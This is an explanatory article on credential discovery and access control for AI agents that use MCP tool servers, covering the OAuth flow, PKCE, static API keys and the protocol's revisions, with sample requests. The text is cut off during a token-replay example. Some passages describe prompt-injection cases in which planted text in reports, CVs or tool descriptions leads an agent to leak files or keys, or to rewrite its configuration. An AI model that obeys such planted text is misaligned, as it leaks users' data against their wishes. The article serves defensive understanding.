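# Credential discovery and access control for AI agents that call third-party web services

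## What an agent needs to know before it calls a web service

Credential discovery is how a program finds out, while it is running, which credential a web service accepts and where to get one. Access control is the set of rules that determine which requests the service carries out. An AI agent is a program in which a language model chooses which actions to take, including calls to outside services. This makes both credential discovery and access control harder, because the agent's developer never saw many of those services.

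Suppose a user asks an agent to read the sales reports in an online file store and mail a summary to a colleague. The agent has to find out which operations the store offers, such as listing, searching or deleting files, as well as which credential it accepts and who issues that credential. The store has to identify the client, because the request comes from software it has never dealt with. Somebody also has to judge whether the action is what the user wanted, which is only to send this summary to this colleague. Settling one of these questions doesn't settle the others. Even if the store describes itself accurately and accepts a valid credential, the program that presented the credential could still mail the reports to a stranger.

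### Tools, clients and tool servers

Much of the recent work on these questions concerns the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open protocol that Anthropic released in November 2024 and that was last revised on 28 July 2026. Anthropic reported more than 950 MCP servers in the directory of its assistant Claude (*Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude*, 2026). The Model Context Protocol project (2026) reported close to half a billion monthly downloads of its main software kits, but this figure is only a loose measure of use because automated builds download the same package many times.

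The Model Context Protocol (MCP) lets agents list and call tools offered by programs called tool servers. A tool is an operation that the model can call, and it has a name, a text description and a schema for its inputs. When a client sends a `tools/list` request, the server replies with a list of its tools. In an example from the Model Context Protocol (2026) specification, the reply includes a tool named `get_weather` and a sentence about what it does. The Model Context Protocol documentation says tools are designed to be "model-controlled", meaning that the model finds and invokes them based on its own reading of the context.

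Two more pieces of software sit between the model and the server. The Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026) describes a host, the application the user runs, which creates one client for each server. The client connects to that server on the agent's behalf and holds the credentials for it. In the example, the host would run one client for the file store and another for the mail service. Neither server should have access to the whole conversation or to the other server. The reports therefore reach the mail service only through the host and the model, so the model's context is where text from the file store can affect what happens to the user's mail.

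### Authentication and authorization

Authentication establishes who somebody is, and authorization establishes what that person, or a program acting on their behalf, may do. The file store can already authenticate its user, but it has no way to determine how much of the user's access this agent should have.

Giving an agent the user's password is a crude solution. *The OAuth 2.1 Authorization Framework* (Hardt, Parecki and Lodderstedt, 2026) explains that the application then has to store the password and gains far more access than it needs, and that the user can shut it out only by changing the password, which shuts out every other application using it. OAuth, a standard of which this is the latest draft, replaces the password with an access token, a usually short-lived credential that carries a limited part of the user's access. The draft states that OAuth is not an authentication protocol,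 so a client that needs to identify the user requires an addition such as OpenID Connect, which builds on OAuth.

The Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026) uses OAuth's roles. The tool server is the resource server, which guards the files and accepts tokens, and the user is the resource owner. The authorization server signs the user in, asks for consent and issues access tokens. It may belong to the same company as the tool server or to a different one. Support for authorization is optional in the Model Context Protocol (MCP), and these rules apply to servers that clients reach over HTTP. A client that communicates with a program on the user's machine through standard input and output takes credentials from the local environment instead.

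### The authorization-code flow

The usual way to obtain a token on a user's behalf is the authorization-code flow. For the file store it runs as follows.

1. The client calls the store without a credential. The store refuses with HTTP status 401 and points to its protected resource metadata, a document that names the authorization servers it accepts.
2. The client generates a random secret, the code verifier, and computes a hash of it, the code challenge. It keeps the verifier to itself.
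3. The client redirects the user, opening a browser at the authorization server. The address carries the client's identifier, the code challenge, a return address, the name of the service the token is for, and the scope the client wants. A scope is a named permission such as `files:read`.
4. The user signs in and sees a consent page, which should show who is asking and for what. The client never sees the password, and the authorization server can demand a second factor without the client's involvement.
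5. If the user agrees, the authorization server sends the browser back to the return address with an authorization code. It should add its issuer, the URL that identifies it. The code opens nothing by itself, and Hardt and colleagues recommend that it expire within ten minutes.
6. The client sends the code and the verifier directly to the authorization server. The server hashes the verifier and compares the result with the challenge from the redirect. If they match, it returns an access token, and perhaps a refresh token with which the client can later get a new one.
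7. The client repeats its original call with the access token in a header. The store checks that the token has not expired, that its scope covers the request, and that the store is its audience, meaning the service for which the authorization server issued it. Then it returns the file.

This flow sends only the code through the browser because page addresses end up in browsing histories and server logs, where an attacker may find them. The authorization server sends the token directly to the client.

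That leaves the danger that somebody steals the code. The verifier and challenge, together known as PKCE (Proof Key for Code Exchange), deal with it. The computation is one line:

`code_challenge = BASE64URL(SHA256(code_verifier))`

The verifier is a new random string of 43 to 128 characters for each sign-in. SHA-256 is a one-way function, so a thief who reads the challenge cannot work back to the verifier. BASE64URL rewrites the hash in characters that are safe in a web address. A thief who has only the code gets an error. The same comparison also protects against an attacker who plants a code from their own sign-in in the victim's client, because that code belongs to a different challenge and the authorization server rejects it. PKCE began as a protection for native apps, and Hardt and colleagues now require it of almost every client. The November 2025 revision of the Model Context Protocol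 also requires clients to stop if the authorization server's metadata does not show support for PKCE.

PKCE proves that the program redeeming the authorization code is the one that began the sign-in. It gives no evidence of who wrote that program, because a hostile client can generate a verifier as easily as an honest one can.

### What scope, audience and issuer each rule out

OAuth doesn't define specific scopes. Each authorization server defines its own, and it may grant a narrower scope than the client requested if it tells the client. The tool server enforces the scope. If an agent with a token for `files:read` tries to overwrite a report, the server should return status 403 with the error `insufficient_scope`. The amount of protection depends on how finely the service divides its permissions. For instance, a scope that allows a client to send mail normally doesn't restrict who can receive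 it.

A token's audience matters because most access tokens are bearer tokens, which anyone holding them can use. The operator of a dishonest file store could take the token it receives and try it at the mail service. To prevent this, the Model Context Protocol (MCP) requires the client to name the intended server in a `resource` parameter, both in the redirect and in the token exchange. The server must refuse any token issued for another recipient and must not pass such tokens on. However, clients must send the parameter even if the authorization server doesn't support it, and an authorization server that ignores it may issue a token that isn't restricted to the intended server.

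Checking the issuer protects a client that deals with many authorization servers, as an agent's client will. Before the redirect, the client records the issuer it expects. When the browser returns with an issuer value, the client compares the two character by character and rejects the response if they differ. This check helps only if the recorded value is authentic, which the client can't assume if it took the value from an unchecked source.

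### What changes when an agent is calling

The developer of an ordinary app does most of the discovery by hand. Before any user signs in, the developer reads the service's documentation, registers the app, receives a client identifier, chooses the scopes and writes the authorization server's address into the code. This manual work allowed OAuth to leave client registration and endpoint discovery partly undefined, and Hardt and colleagues still leave them to optional extensions.

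An agent first encounters the service at run time. The November 2025 revision of the Model Context Protocol describes this as the most common case, in which client and server have no prior relationship. It also states that a general-purpose client usually lacks the domain knowledge to choose scopes. The client therefore requests the scopes listed in the server's refusal or, if none are listed there, every scope in the server's metadata. This is a sensible default for a client with no information about the service, but it leaves the user to judge the request on a consent page, perhaps in the middle of another task.

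The service also lacks reliable information about the client. MCP requests normally include a client name and version, but according to the Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026), the sender supplies both, the protocol does not verify them, and they should not be used for security decisions. A typical deployment also involves more than a user and an application, and its trust relationships may cross organizational boundaries, according to Tabata's *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28* (2026). At each boundary, one party must either trust another's description of itself or find a way to check it.

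The other difference is that an ordinary app makes the calls its developer wrote, while an agent chooses its calls by reading text. Other people wrote much of that text, including tool descriptions, search results, and the reports in the file store.

Prompt injection is an attack in which a model follows text from an untrusted source as if it were an instruction. In the indirect form, the attacker has no access to the AI system and leaves the text where the system will read it. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post by David C for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a job applicant who hides a line in a CV telling the screening model to approve the application.

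A confused deputy is a program that someone tricks into using its legitimate authority for their own purpose. The name comes from Hardy's 1988 account, *The Confused Deputy*, which describes a compiler on a shared computer. The compiler had permission to update the system's billing file. Lecture slides also titled *The Confused Deputy* explain that a user could name that file as the destination for debugging output. The compiler then overwrote the billing records, and the operating system's access check succeeded because the compiler was allowed to write there.

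An agent can fail in the same way. Suppose one of the sales reports contains a sentence telling the reader to send all the reports to an outside address, and the model complies. The file store and the mail service each receive a valid token with the right scope and audience, and every check in the authorization-code flow passes, but the user's data has been leaked.

A programmer can fix Hardy's problem by making the compiler check whose authority it is using for which file. David C argues that a language model, by contrast, is "inherently confusable", because it predicts the next token from all the text so far and cannot keep commands and data apart as a database can. Researchers have tried to detect injected text, mark untrusted passages, and train models to give priority to genuine instructions, but in his view each of these overlays a distinction that the technology lacks. He bases this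 on how the models work, and concludes only that injection may never be fully preventable. His advice holds even if he is too pessimistic. Designers should assume that an attacker can use any tool the model can use, and should limit the damage with safeguards outside the model. Scope is useful for this even though it cannot distinguish a wanted email from an unwanted one, because an agent with no permission to delete files cannot delete them, even if someone has deceived it.

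The host is mainly responsible for checking what the user wanted. The November 2025 overview of the Model Context Protocol (2025) calls for users to understand and consent to all data access and operations, and the protocol's architecture makes the host responsible for enforcing consent. Consent at sign-in is a weak form of this, because a user who approves `files:read` approves a kind of action before the agent has chosen a specific one.

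### Who might attack

Three parties can exploit this arrangement, and they start from different positions.

The operator of a hostile tool server writes the tool descriptions, names the authorization servers and receives whatever token the client sends. The operator may try to use that token at other services, which audience checks are meant to prevent. The operator can also put malicious instructions in the tool descriptions, which the model reads before it calls any tool.

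Conversely, a hostile client can attack an honest service. PortSwigger's *MCP server vulnerabilities* notes that an MCP server is a web API and accepts requests from any program that can send them, with or without an AI assistant. The attacker can also trick a user into granting access. In what Hardt and colleagues call consent phishing, the attacker registers a client with a legitimate authorization server and sends the victim a genuine sign-in link. The victim signs in at the real site and then approves the attacker's client. Strong authentication, such as a phishing-resistant hardware key, doesn't prevent this because the deception happens at the authorization step.

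An attacker can feed content to the agent by sharing a file with the user, sending an email or publishing a web page that the agent will open, all without running a server or a client. This attacker never holds a token or takes part in the authorization-code flow, so neither the tool server nor the authorization server can block them by denying access.

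## Manifests and static keys, before 2025 and still in use

Before agents had their own protocol, many web services published OpenAPI documents, which list a service's operations with their inputs and outputs in a standard format. An OpenAPI document is a descriptor, a machine-readable account of what a service offers and how to reach it. It can also describe credentials, in entries called security schemes.

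### What an OpenAPI document gives a program

For the file store, the relevant lines might look like this.

```yaml
components:
  securitySchemes:
    storeKey:
      type: apiKey
      in: header
      name: X-Store-Key
security:
  - storeKey: []
```

The upper block defines a scheme, and the last two lines apply it to every operation. An API key is a secret string that a service issues to a caller, much like a password. A program can work out from these lines that every request needs an `X-Store-Key` header containing the key, but not how to get a key. The OpenAPI Initiative's *Describing API Security* has a similar sample with the note "API key provided in console", which is a hint for a person, who has to sign in to a website and copy the key. The guide puts onboarding and key exchange outside the format's scope.

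The format supports four other types of security: HTTP authentication (a password or a bearer token), mutual TLS (client and server both present certificates), OAuth and OpenID Connect. An OAuth entry is much more informative than an API-key entry. It lists the authorization server's endpoints and can list the scopes. Each operation can also name the scopes it needs, so a client that only reads data can avoid requesting write permission. An OpenID Connect entry links to the identity provider's metadata document. OpenAPI 3.2 has a comparable field for OAuth, which holds the address of the authorization server's metadata, according to Microsoft's *OpenApiSecurityScheme.OAuth2MetadataUrl Property*.

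With such an entry, a program can send the user to the right place to sign in. It still has no client identifier, and OpenAPI has no step for obtaining one, so a developer has to register the program first.

### OpenAI's plugin manifest

In 2023 OpenAI built a format on top of OpenAPI for describing web services to language models. To work with ChatGPT, a service published a manifest, `ai-plugin.json`, under `/.well-known/` on its own site. The manifest held a description for the model, a link to the service's OpenAPI document and an `auth` field. In March 2023 the programmer Simon Willison published one for Datasette, a tool for querying databases, with the `auth` type "none". Because the path was the same on every site, he could also look up Wolfram Alpha's manifest.

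In *ChatGPT Plugin Examples*, breadchris (2023) copied a to-do list plugin from OpenAI's documentation. The block below comes from that plugin, with a placeholder replacing the token.

```json
"auth": {
  "type": "service_http",
  "authorization_type": "bearer",
  "verification_tokens": {
    "openai": "TOKEN_FROM_CHATGPT"
  }
}
```

This told ChatGPT to send a bearer token with each request, but a person had to supply the token. According to OpenAI's instructions, as developers quoted them in the forum thread *Service level authentication*, the developer could enter a client secret while installing the plugin. ChatGPT's web interface then generated a verification token, which the developer pasted into the manifest. Anyone could read the manifest, so the verification token can't have been the secret that protected the service. Presumably it showed OpenAI that the person installing the plugin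 also controlled the site.

A shared secret of this kind identifies ChatGPT but not the user. In the to-do example, the username is part of the web address, and the OpenAPI document includes an instruction for the model to ask the user for it. Anyone who gave ChatGPT another person's username would have received that person's list. The plugin is only a teaching example, but it shows how a service can authenticate the client correctly and still have no basis for deciding whose data to return.

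Plugins that handled personal data could use OAuth instead. *Security study based on the Chatgptplugin system* (2025) describes it as one of the three main options, along with bearer tokens and no authentication. For OAuth, the manifest gave the address of the sign-in page, the endpoint for exchanging the authorization code and the scope. The developer also had to register a client identifier and secret with OpenAI manually, and a sample block in the forum thread *Has anyone got ChatGPT plugin to work with OAuth?* has the same slot for a verification token from ChatGPT's interface. According to *LLM Platform Security* (2023), OpenAI reviewed each plugin, listed it in a store and supplied the interface through which users signed in.

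This worked because ChatGPT was the only client and each service's developer dealt with OpenAI in advance. Another company's agent could read the same manifest and learn the kind of credential required and the relevant addresses, but it would have had no secret or client identifier.

OpenAI closed the plugin store to new installations on 19 March 2024 and ended the remaining plugin conversations on 9 April, according to a forum notice, *Plugin Store and New Chats With Plugins*. OpenAI's current plugins share little with the old ones besides the name. They use MCP servers and MCP's authorization rules, as OpenAI's *Authentication* explains, and their manifest rejects a client secret. Some old manifests are still online, and *Well-Known Agent Files*, from the website auditing tool squirrelscan, advises owners to delete them because they are more likely to confuse an agent than to help it.

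### The first MCP release and the local server

The first revision of the MCP specification, dated 5 November 2024, had no authorization framework. The Model Context Protocol (2025) lists its addition among the March 2025 changes. The omission made some sense at the time because, according to AWS's *Open Protocols for Agent Interoperability Part 2*, users at first downloaded tool servers and ran them on their own machines. A server that accepts input only from the program that started it has no other callers to authenticate.

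The local server still needs a credential for the service behind it. *State of MCP Server Security 2025* (Skverer, 2025), a study for the security company Astrix, reports that the first specification didn't cover where to keep this credential, and that almost all of the first sample servers used broad credentials that never expire. The GitHub and GitLab samples took personal access tokens, which users generate in their account settings, and the Postgres database sample took a username and password.

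A typical configuration for a local server looks like this.

```json
"mcpServers": {
  "file-store": {
    "command": "python",
    "args": ["store_server.py"],
    "env": { "STORE_KEY": "the-actual-key" }
  }
}
```

When the host application starts, it reads this file and runs the command with `STORE_KEY` set as an environment variable, a named value that the operating system passes to a program at launch. The server reads the variable and puts the key in its requests to the file store, so the key never has to appear in the model's input.

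The November 2025 revision of the Model Context Protocol kept this pattern from the first release. Many services behind the servers leave little choice because they accept only API keys and don't support OAuth, as the security firm Trail of Bits points out in *Insecure credential storage plagues MCP* (2025). A directory cited in Trend Micro's *Beware of MCP Hardcoded Credentials* grew from 714 servers in January 2025 to 16,098 in July.

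### Who can read the key

Desktop operating systems mostly decide who may open a file by user account. A program that the user starts, such as a game, a browser helper or a software package's installation script, runs under the user's account, so it can normally open whatever the user can, including the configuration file. Restricting the file's permissions to its owner keeps out other people who use the machine, but not other programs that the owner runs. The files are also easy to find, because each host application keeps them in a standard location. The security vendor MCProtect's *State of MCP Security* adds that they end up in cloud synchronization, in backups and in the public repositories where programmers share their settings.

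Removing the key from the file only partly protects it. MCProtect recommends storing the key in the macOS keychain and loading it into an environment variable when the user opens a terminal. Accidentally uploading the file then no longer exposes the key, but every program started from that terminal inherits the variable. On Linux, a program can also normally read the initial environment of another program running under the same account. Astrix offers a wrapper that fetches the key from an online vault and places it in the server's environment at launch. This keeps the key off the disk but not out of the environment, and Skverer concedes that the wrapper doesn't narrow the key's permissions or shorten its lifetime.

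The agent is one of the programs that can read the key. If it has a tool for opening files or running commands, a prompt injection can lead it to open the configuration file and send the contents elsewhere. Doerrfeld (2026) reports in *7 Common MCP Security Flaws and Vulnerabilities* that the security organization OWASP puts token mismanagement and secret exposure first in its draft list of MCP risks and includes prompt injection among the ways to extract tokens.

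A stolen key is usually more useful to a thief than a stolen access token, because the key may work for years and often covers a whole account.

### How common static keys are

Two studies have tried to measure this, both by security companies that sell products for managing such credentials. The companies had an interest in alarming results, but in both cases they disclosed enough about their methods to allow some checking.

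Help Net Security's *Hardcoded MCP credentials found in public GitHub files* describes a September 2026 study by Hush Security, which searched public GitHub repositories for the configuration filenames that major coding agents use and analyzed about 82,000 files. Hush recorded whether each credential slot held an actual value, a reference to an environment variable or secret manager, a prompt for the user, a placeholder or nothing. It found a hard-coded credential in 12% of the slots.

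To tell a key from ordinary text, Hush looked for the formats that particular providers use and measured the text's Shannon entropy:

`H = −Σ p(c) · log2 p(c)`

Here p(c) is the share of the string made up of the character c. The word "password" scores 2.75 bits per character, while a long random string of the digits 0–9 and letters a–f scores close to 4. Entropy is only a hint, because harmless identifiers can look random too. For the 55% of hard-coded secrets whose format did not identify a provider, Hush also relied on the slot's name and the value's length and character patterns. Hush concluded that almost all of these were real secrets, but it did not test any of them with a service, so it is not known how many still worked.

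Hush found that 24% of all the hard-coded credentials were of a type that is both broad and non-expiring by design. Of the credentials whose scope it could classify, 53% gave access to an entire organization, account, workspace or database. Of the credentials with a defined expiry policy, 80% did not expire by default. Quoting the last two figures as shares of all the credentials would exaggerate the finding.

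Hush also searched up to seven past revisions of 7,681 configurations that contained credentials. In 243 of them, about 3%, an earlier version still contained a secret that someone had deleted from the current file. Deleting a leaked key from the file therefore isn't enough, and the owner has to replace it at the provider.

Hush's count of exposed credentials is a lower bound because GitHub's search omits forks, covers only each repository's default branch and caps the results of each query. Hush also treats the 12% as a lower bound, but a partial sample can make a percentage too high or too low. People who publish a configuration file may also be more careful with it than people who keep theirs private, so the share on ordinary machines may be higher.

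For Astrix's 2025 study of which credentials the servers request, Skverer collected 5,205 repositories of open-source servers from GitHub, downloaded their README files and had a language model classify them. By this count, 88% of servers needed credentials. About 53% used static keys or personal access tokens, and 8.5% used OAuth. Among API keys, 79% reached the server through plain environment variables.

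The usual figure of 5,200 servers is too high, because about 30% of the repositories did not contain a real server, which leaves roughly 3,600. The language model also classified 26.4% of the servers as "unknown", and Skverer admits that it probably misjudged whether some servers need credentials. He does not compare its results with human judgments. Even so, the ranking is fairly robust to the unknown cases. If all of them used OAuth, the OAuth share would rise to about 35%, still well below 53%.

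The sample favors popular repositories and counts each server once, however many people use it. It also poorly represents the remote servers that companies operate. A later survey of live servers is better evidence for those.

The 53% and 12% figures are consistent, because a server may require a static key that its user supplies by reference. Astrix would count that key as static, but Hush would not count it as hard-coded. MCProtect blurs this distinction when it cites Astrix for the claim that 53% of servers use "plaintext" keys. Skverer's 53% describes how long the credentials last, regardless of how they appear in the file.

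### When the configuration file runs a command

The same configuration file contains the command that starts the server, so anyone who can edit the file can run a program on the machine. In April 2026, OX Security's *The Mother of All AI Supply Chains* called this a critical flaw in Anthropic's official software development kits for MCP. The kits run whatever command the file contains. If the command doesn't start a tool server, the client gets an error, but only after the command has run. A hostile command has the same permissions as the program that launched it, so it can usually access all the keys described above.

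OX reported running commands on six live commercial platforms. It said up to 200,000 installations were vulnerable and cited 150 million downloads. These totals indicate how widely the software is used rather than how many systems are open to attack. An attacker needs a way to get text into the configuration, and there is none if the developer writes the command into the program and accepts no outside input.

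Anthropic declined to change the design. ITPro's *AI agents using Anthropic MCP could be a vector* quotes it telling OX that this was not a valid vulnerability because it "requires explicit user permission for the file change". Anthropic later updated its security policy to advise caution with local servers and to make developers responsible for securing their code. OX replied that developers are not security engineers and that tens of thousands of them can't each be expected to find and fix the same problem.

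Anthropic has a point about the mechanism, because software that launches local programs has to run commands, and the kit has no way to distinguish wanted commands from unwanted ones. But Anthropic's reply depends on a user who sees the change and can refuse it, and OX Security describes cases without such a user. On some of the web platforms, an outsider could submit a configuration that ran on the company's server, so asking the outsider for approval would not protect the company. In the code editor Windsurf, according to OX Security, injected text led the agent to rewrite the configuration file without showing the user the change, and the new command then ran with no further action by the user.

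OX proposed that the kits accept only commands from a list that the developer sets in advance, or that they require developers to explicitly switch on an unsafe mode. Having to switch on that mode would at least warn developers who don't realize that the configuration is executable. A list that covers only program names can be evaded, as OX showed in one product where a permitted program could start other programs. A list that also fixed each program's arguments would be harder to evade, but it would make new servers more cumbersome to add.

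The MCP specification addressed the consent problem before OX published. Under its November 2025 revision, clients should get the user's explicit consent before they install or run a local server, according to Auth0's *Model Context Protocol Nov 2025 Specification Update* (2026). Whether users see that consent request depends on the company that writes the client.

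## How a tool server tells a client where to get a token, March to June 2025

A local tool server gets its key from the program that starts it. But a tool server that a company runs on the internet receives HTTP requests from clients it has no record of, and those clients have to find out where to get a token. In 2025, the Model Context Protocol (MCP) project specified two different ways for them to do this, less than three months apart.

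### Default paths in the March revision

The revision of 26 March 2025 introduced OAuth 2.1 and a rule for finding the authorization server. The client takes the tool server's address and drops the path. In the Model Context Protocol's example, a tool server at `https://api.example.com/v1/mcp` has its authorization server at `https://api.example.com`. The client first looks there for authorization server metadata, a document that lists the authorization server's endpoints and features. The format comes from RFC 8414, one of the numbered documents in which the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF) publishes internet standards. If the client doesn't find the metadata, it falls back on three default addresses:

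```
https://api.example.com/authorize
https://api.example.com/token
https://api.example.com/register
```

The user signs in at the first address. The client exchanges the authorization code for a token at the second and registers itself at the third. The revision required clients to look for the metadata but only recommended that servers publish it, so a developer could set up a working server with just these three endpoints.

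The rule needs no configuration, but it assumes that the tool server's host also has an authorization server. The revision allowed developers to run the authorization server as a separate service, but its example put both roles in one program, and a tool server had no field for naming an authorization server on another host.

### Tool servers that had to issue tokens

Many companies already have an identity provider, a service such as Microsoft's Entra ID that signs their staff in to other software. It runs on its own host, so the March rule couldn't lead a client to it. The revision offered developers a third-party flow instead:

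1. The client starts a sign-in with the tool server.
2. The tool server redirects the user to the identity provider, where the user signs in and agrees.
3. The identity provider sends the browser back to the tool server with an authorization code, and the tool server exchanges the code for the provider's access token.
4. The tool server creates an access token of its own, ties it to the provider's token and gives it to the client.

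The tool server is now both an OAuth client of the provider and an authorization server for its own clients. This takes a lot of security code for a program that lists and reads files. The server has to store the provider's token securely, record which of its own tokens corresponds to it, and check that the provider's token is still valid before accepting its own. Without that check, if an employee leaves and the identity provider cancels the employee's token, the tool server will go on accepting the token it issued.

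*Improving The Model Context Protocol Authorization Spec*, a developer's account on den.dev, describes running into "a few walls" while trying to connect GitHub and Entra ID to this design. The developer joined identity and security specialists in drafting a proposal to change the specification rather than rely on workarounds.

In *Let's fix OAuth in MCP*, Parecki (2025) blamed the specification's text and diagrams, which showed the tool server itself handling authorization. OAuth doesn't require this, because it treats the authorization server and the resource server as separate roles. Parecki, who co-wrote the OAuth 2.1 draft, thinks of the authorization server as a "token factory". On this view, a tool server only has to check that a token is valid, and a separate server can issue it.

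### The split in June

When the March revision came out, services had no standard way to name their authorization servers. The IETF (2025) published one a few weeks later, in April, as RFC 9728, which defines the format of protected resource metadata.

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) revision of 18 June 2025 classifies tool servers as OAuth resource servers and adds protected resource metadata so that clients can find the authorization server (Model Context Protocol, *Key Changes*, 2025). Parecki (2025) wrote that day that tool servers no longer issue tokens or sign users in. MCP still lets one company run both the tool server and the authorization server. The revision also removed the default paths and required authorization servers to publish their metadata.

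The new document also solved a problem with shared hosts. A hosting company might run tool servers for two customers at `/customer1/mcp` and `/customer2/mcp`. The March rule dropped the path, so it sent both customers' clients to the same authorization server, even if the customers used different identity providers. *OAuth 2.0 Protected Resource Metadata* (RFC 9728), by Jones, Hunt and Parecki, gives each path its own metadata address and notes that some hosting arrangements with many customers require this.

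The June revision also required clients to name the intended tool server in the `resource` parameter, which comes from another standard, RFC 8707. The parameter is meant to stop a token issued for one server from working anywhere else. According to the list of changes, the requirement prevents malicious servers from obtaining access tokens, but that is too strong, because a malicious server still receives any token that a client gets for it.

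Parts of the March design remain in some software. The Model Context Protocol's Python software development kit has a setting that embeds a complete authorization server in a tool server, though the documentation advises against using this setting for new servers.

### One exchange from start to finish

Suppose the file store's tool server is at `https://files.example.com/mcp` and accepts tokens from an authorization server at `https://login.example.net`. The messages below follow the July 2026 rules, with some long values shortened and line breaks added for readability.

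The agent wants to read a report, and its client has no token yet. It sends the call anyway.

```http
POST /mcp HTTP/1.1
Host: files.example.com
MCP-Protocol-Version: 2026-07-28
Mcp-Method: tools/call
Mcp-Name: read_file
Content-Type: application/json

{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 1,
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "read_file",
    "arguments": { "path": "reports/june.csv" },
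    "_meta": {
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/clientInfo": {
        "name": "example-agent",
        "version": "1.0"
      }
    }
  }
}
```

The layout follows a sample in Composio's *The MCP 2026-07-28 Update*. Earlier revisions required the client to open a session first. The July revision removed that step, and each request now includes the details the server needs to process it.

The tool server refuses.

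```http
HTTP/1.1 401 Unauthorized
WWW-Authenticate: Bearer
  resource_metadata="https://files.example.com/.well-known/oauth-protected-resource/mcp",
  scope="files:read"
```

`WWW-Authenticate` is the standard HTTP header for stating what kind of credential a server accepts. RFC 9728 added the `resource_metadata` parameter, which gives the address of the protected resource metadata. The scope is the permission this call needs. In the Python kit, the server refuses the request before any tool runs.

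The client requests that address and receives the following document.

```json
{
  "resource": "https://files.example.com/mcp",
  "authorization_servers": ["https://login.example.net"],
  "scopes_supported": ["files:read"],
  "bearer_methods_supported": ["header"],
  "resource_name": "Example File Store"
}
```

RFC 9728 requires only the `resource` field. MCP also requires `authorization_servers`, with at least one entry. If the field lists several servers, the client chooses which to use and must keep separate credentials for each. The `bearer_methods_supported` field shows that the store accepts tokens in a header, and `resource_name` is a label that the client can show to the user.

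Before using any of this, the client compares the `resource` value with the address it sent its first request to. If the two differ at all, the client must discard the document.

The client now has the issuer, `https://login.example.net`, and builds the address of the authorization server metadata from it.

```http
GET /.well-known/oauth-authorization-server HTTP/1.1
Host: login.example.net
```

The reply contains the addresses that the March revision left clients to guess.

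```json
{
  "issuer": "https://login.example.net",
  "authorization_endpoint": "https://login.example.net/authorize",
  "token_endpoint": "https://login.example.net/token",
  "code_challenge_methods_supported": ["S256"],
  "authorization_response_iss_parameter_supported": true
}
```

The client checks that the issuer is the one it expected. The value `S256` means the authorization server supports PKCE with the SHA-256 hash. By this point the client needs an identifier, here `agent-app`, which it gets by registering with the authorization server.

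Next the client opens the user's browser at this address:

```
https://login.example.net/authorize
  ?response_type=code
  &client_id=agent-app
  &redirect_uri=http%3A%2F%2Flocalhost%3A8765%2Fcallback
  &code_challenge=E9Melhoa2OwvFrEMTJgu...
  &code_challenge_method=S256
  &state=k3v9
  &scope=files%3Aread
  &resource=https%3A%2F%2Ffiles.example.com%2Fmcp
```

The sequences `%3A` and `%2F` stand for a colon and a slash. The return address points to `localhost`, the user's own machine, where the client is waiting. MCP requires HTTPS for any other return address. The `state` value should be random, and the client should discard any response without it. The last line identifies the tool server for which the client is requesting a token.

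After the user signs in and agrees, the client exchanges the authorization code for a token.

```http
POST /token HTTP/1.1
Host: login.example.net
Content-Type: application/x-www-form-urlencoded

grant_type=authorization_code
&client_id=agent-app
&code=Splx...
&code_verifier=dBjftJeZ4CVP...
&resource=https%3A%2F%2Ffiles.example.com%2Fmcp
```

The Model Context Protocol requires the `resource` value in both requests to be a full address, including `https`. Clients should make the address as specific as they can and leave off a final slash unless the slash has a meaning for that server. A server that compares addresses character by character will treat `/mcp` and `/mcp/` as different services.

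The authorization server replies with the token.

```json
{
  "access_token": "eyJhbGciOi...",
  "token_type": "Bearer",
  "expires_in": 3600,
  "scope": "files:read"
}
```

The client then repeats its first request with one extra header:

```http
Authorization: Bearer eyJhbGciOi...
```

The tool server checks the token and returns the report. The client has to include this header in every later request and must never put the token in a URL's query string. When the token expires after an hour, the tool server returns status 401 again, and the client has to get a new token.

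### Where the client looks if the header is missing

In June 2025, MCP required every tool server to put the metadata address in the `WWW-Authenticate` header. RFC 9728 only permits this, as the Model Context Protocol's proposal to align the two points out, and the Model Context Protocol made the header optional in November. A tool server now has to use the header or publish the metadata at a predictable address. Clients have to support both, and the Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Server Discovery* sets the order in which they look:

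1. The client uses the address in the header, if there is one.
2. Otherwise it inserts the well-known path between the host and the tool server's own path, which gives `https://files.example.com/.well-known/oauth-protected-resource/mcp`.
3. If it finds nothing there, it tries the root of the host, `https://files.example.com/.well-known/oauth-protected-resource`.
4. If that fails too, it gives up or uses settings that someone entered in advance.

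Jared Hanson, a co-founder of Keycard, argued on the IETF's OAuth mailing list that the address in the header is mostly redundant. The `resource` value has to match the address the client called, so the client can work out the metadata address. He thought the header was useful only where an application doesn't use well-known addresses, and that a protocol such as MCP could require them.

The client has enough information to find the document without the header, but the header sends it straight to the correct one, so it doesn't have to try two places. Jones and colleagues also allow a service to send a new refusal at any time to signal that its metadata may have changed, after which the client should fetch the document again. A company can therefore move to a different authorization server without contacting the developers of every client.

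A document at the root address in the third step describes the whole host. Its `resource` value must match the address from which the client built its request, so it has to be `https://files.example.com`, without `/mcp`. A host with several tool servers needs a separate document for each path if those servers accept different authorization servers.

Finding the authorization server metadata can also take several attempts. In June 2025, MCP accepted only the RFC 8414 format. Since November, it has also accepted the format of OpenID Connect, which many identity providers already publish, and clients have to support both. For an issuer without a path, the client tries the RFC 8414 address and then the OpenID Connect one. Some identity providers give each customer, or tenant, a path of its own. For `https://auth.example.com/tenant1`, the client has to try three addresses in this order:

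```
https://auth.example.com/.well-known/oauth-authorization-server/tenant1
https://auth.example.com/.well-known/openid-configuration/tenant1
https://auth.example.com/tenant1/.well-known/openid-configuration
```

The last one exists because OpenID Connect appends the well-known path to the end of the issuer URL, while RFC 8414 inserts it after the host.

### One token and two servers

The `resource` parameter and the audience check guard against an attack that RFC 9728 describes in its security section. Suppose server A, a hostile tool server at `https://a.example.org/mcp`, offers a free calendar, and its operator wants the user's files from server B, the file store.

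When the client calls A, A rejects the call and requests the scope `files:read`, which is unrelated to calendars. A's metadata lists `https://login.example.net`, the authorization server that B uses. The user sees the genuine sign-in page and agrees, perhaps without reading closely. The client sends the new token to A, and A's operator presents it to B.

An access token can be a signed document that the receiving server reads for itself. Decoded, this one might contain the following.

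```json
{
  "iss": "https://login.example.net",
  "aud": "https://a.example.org/mcp",
  "scope": "files:read",
  "exp": 1785200400
}
```

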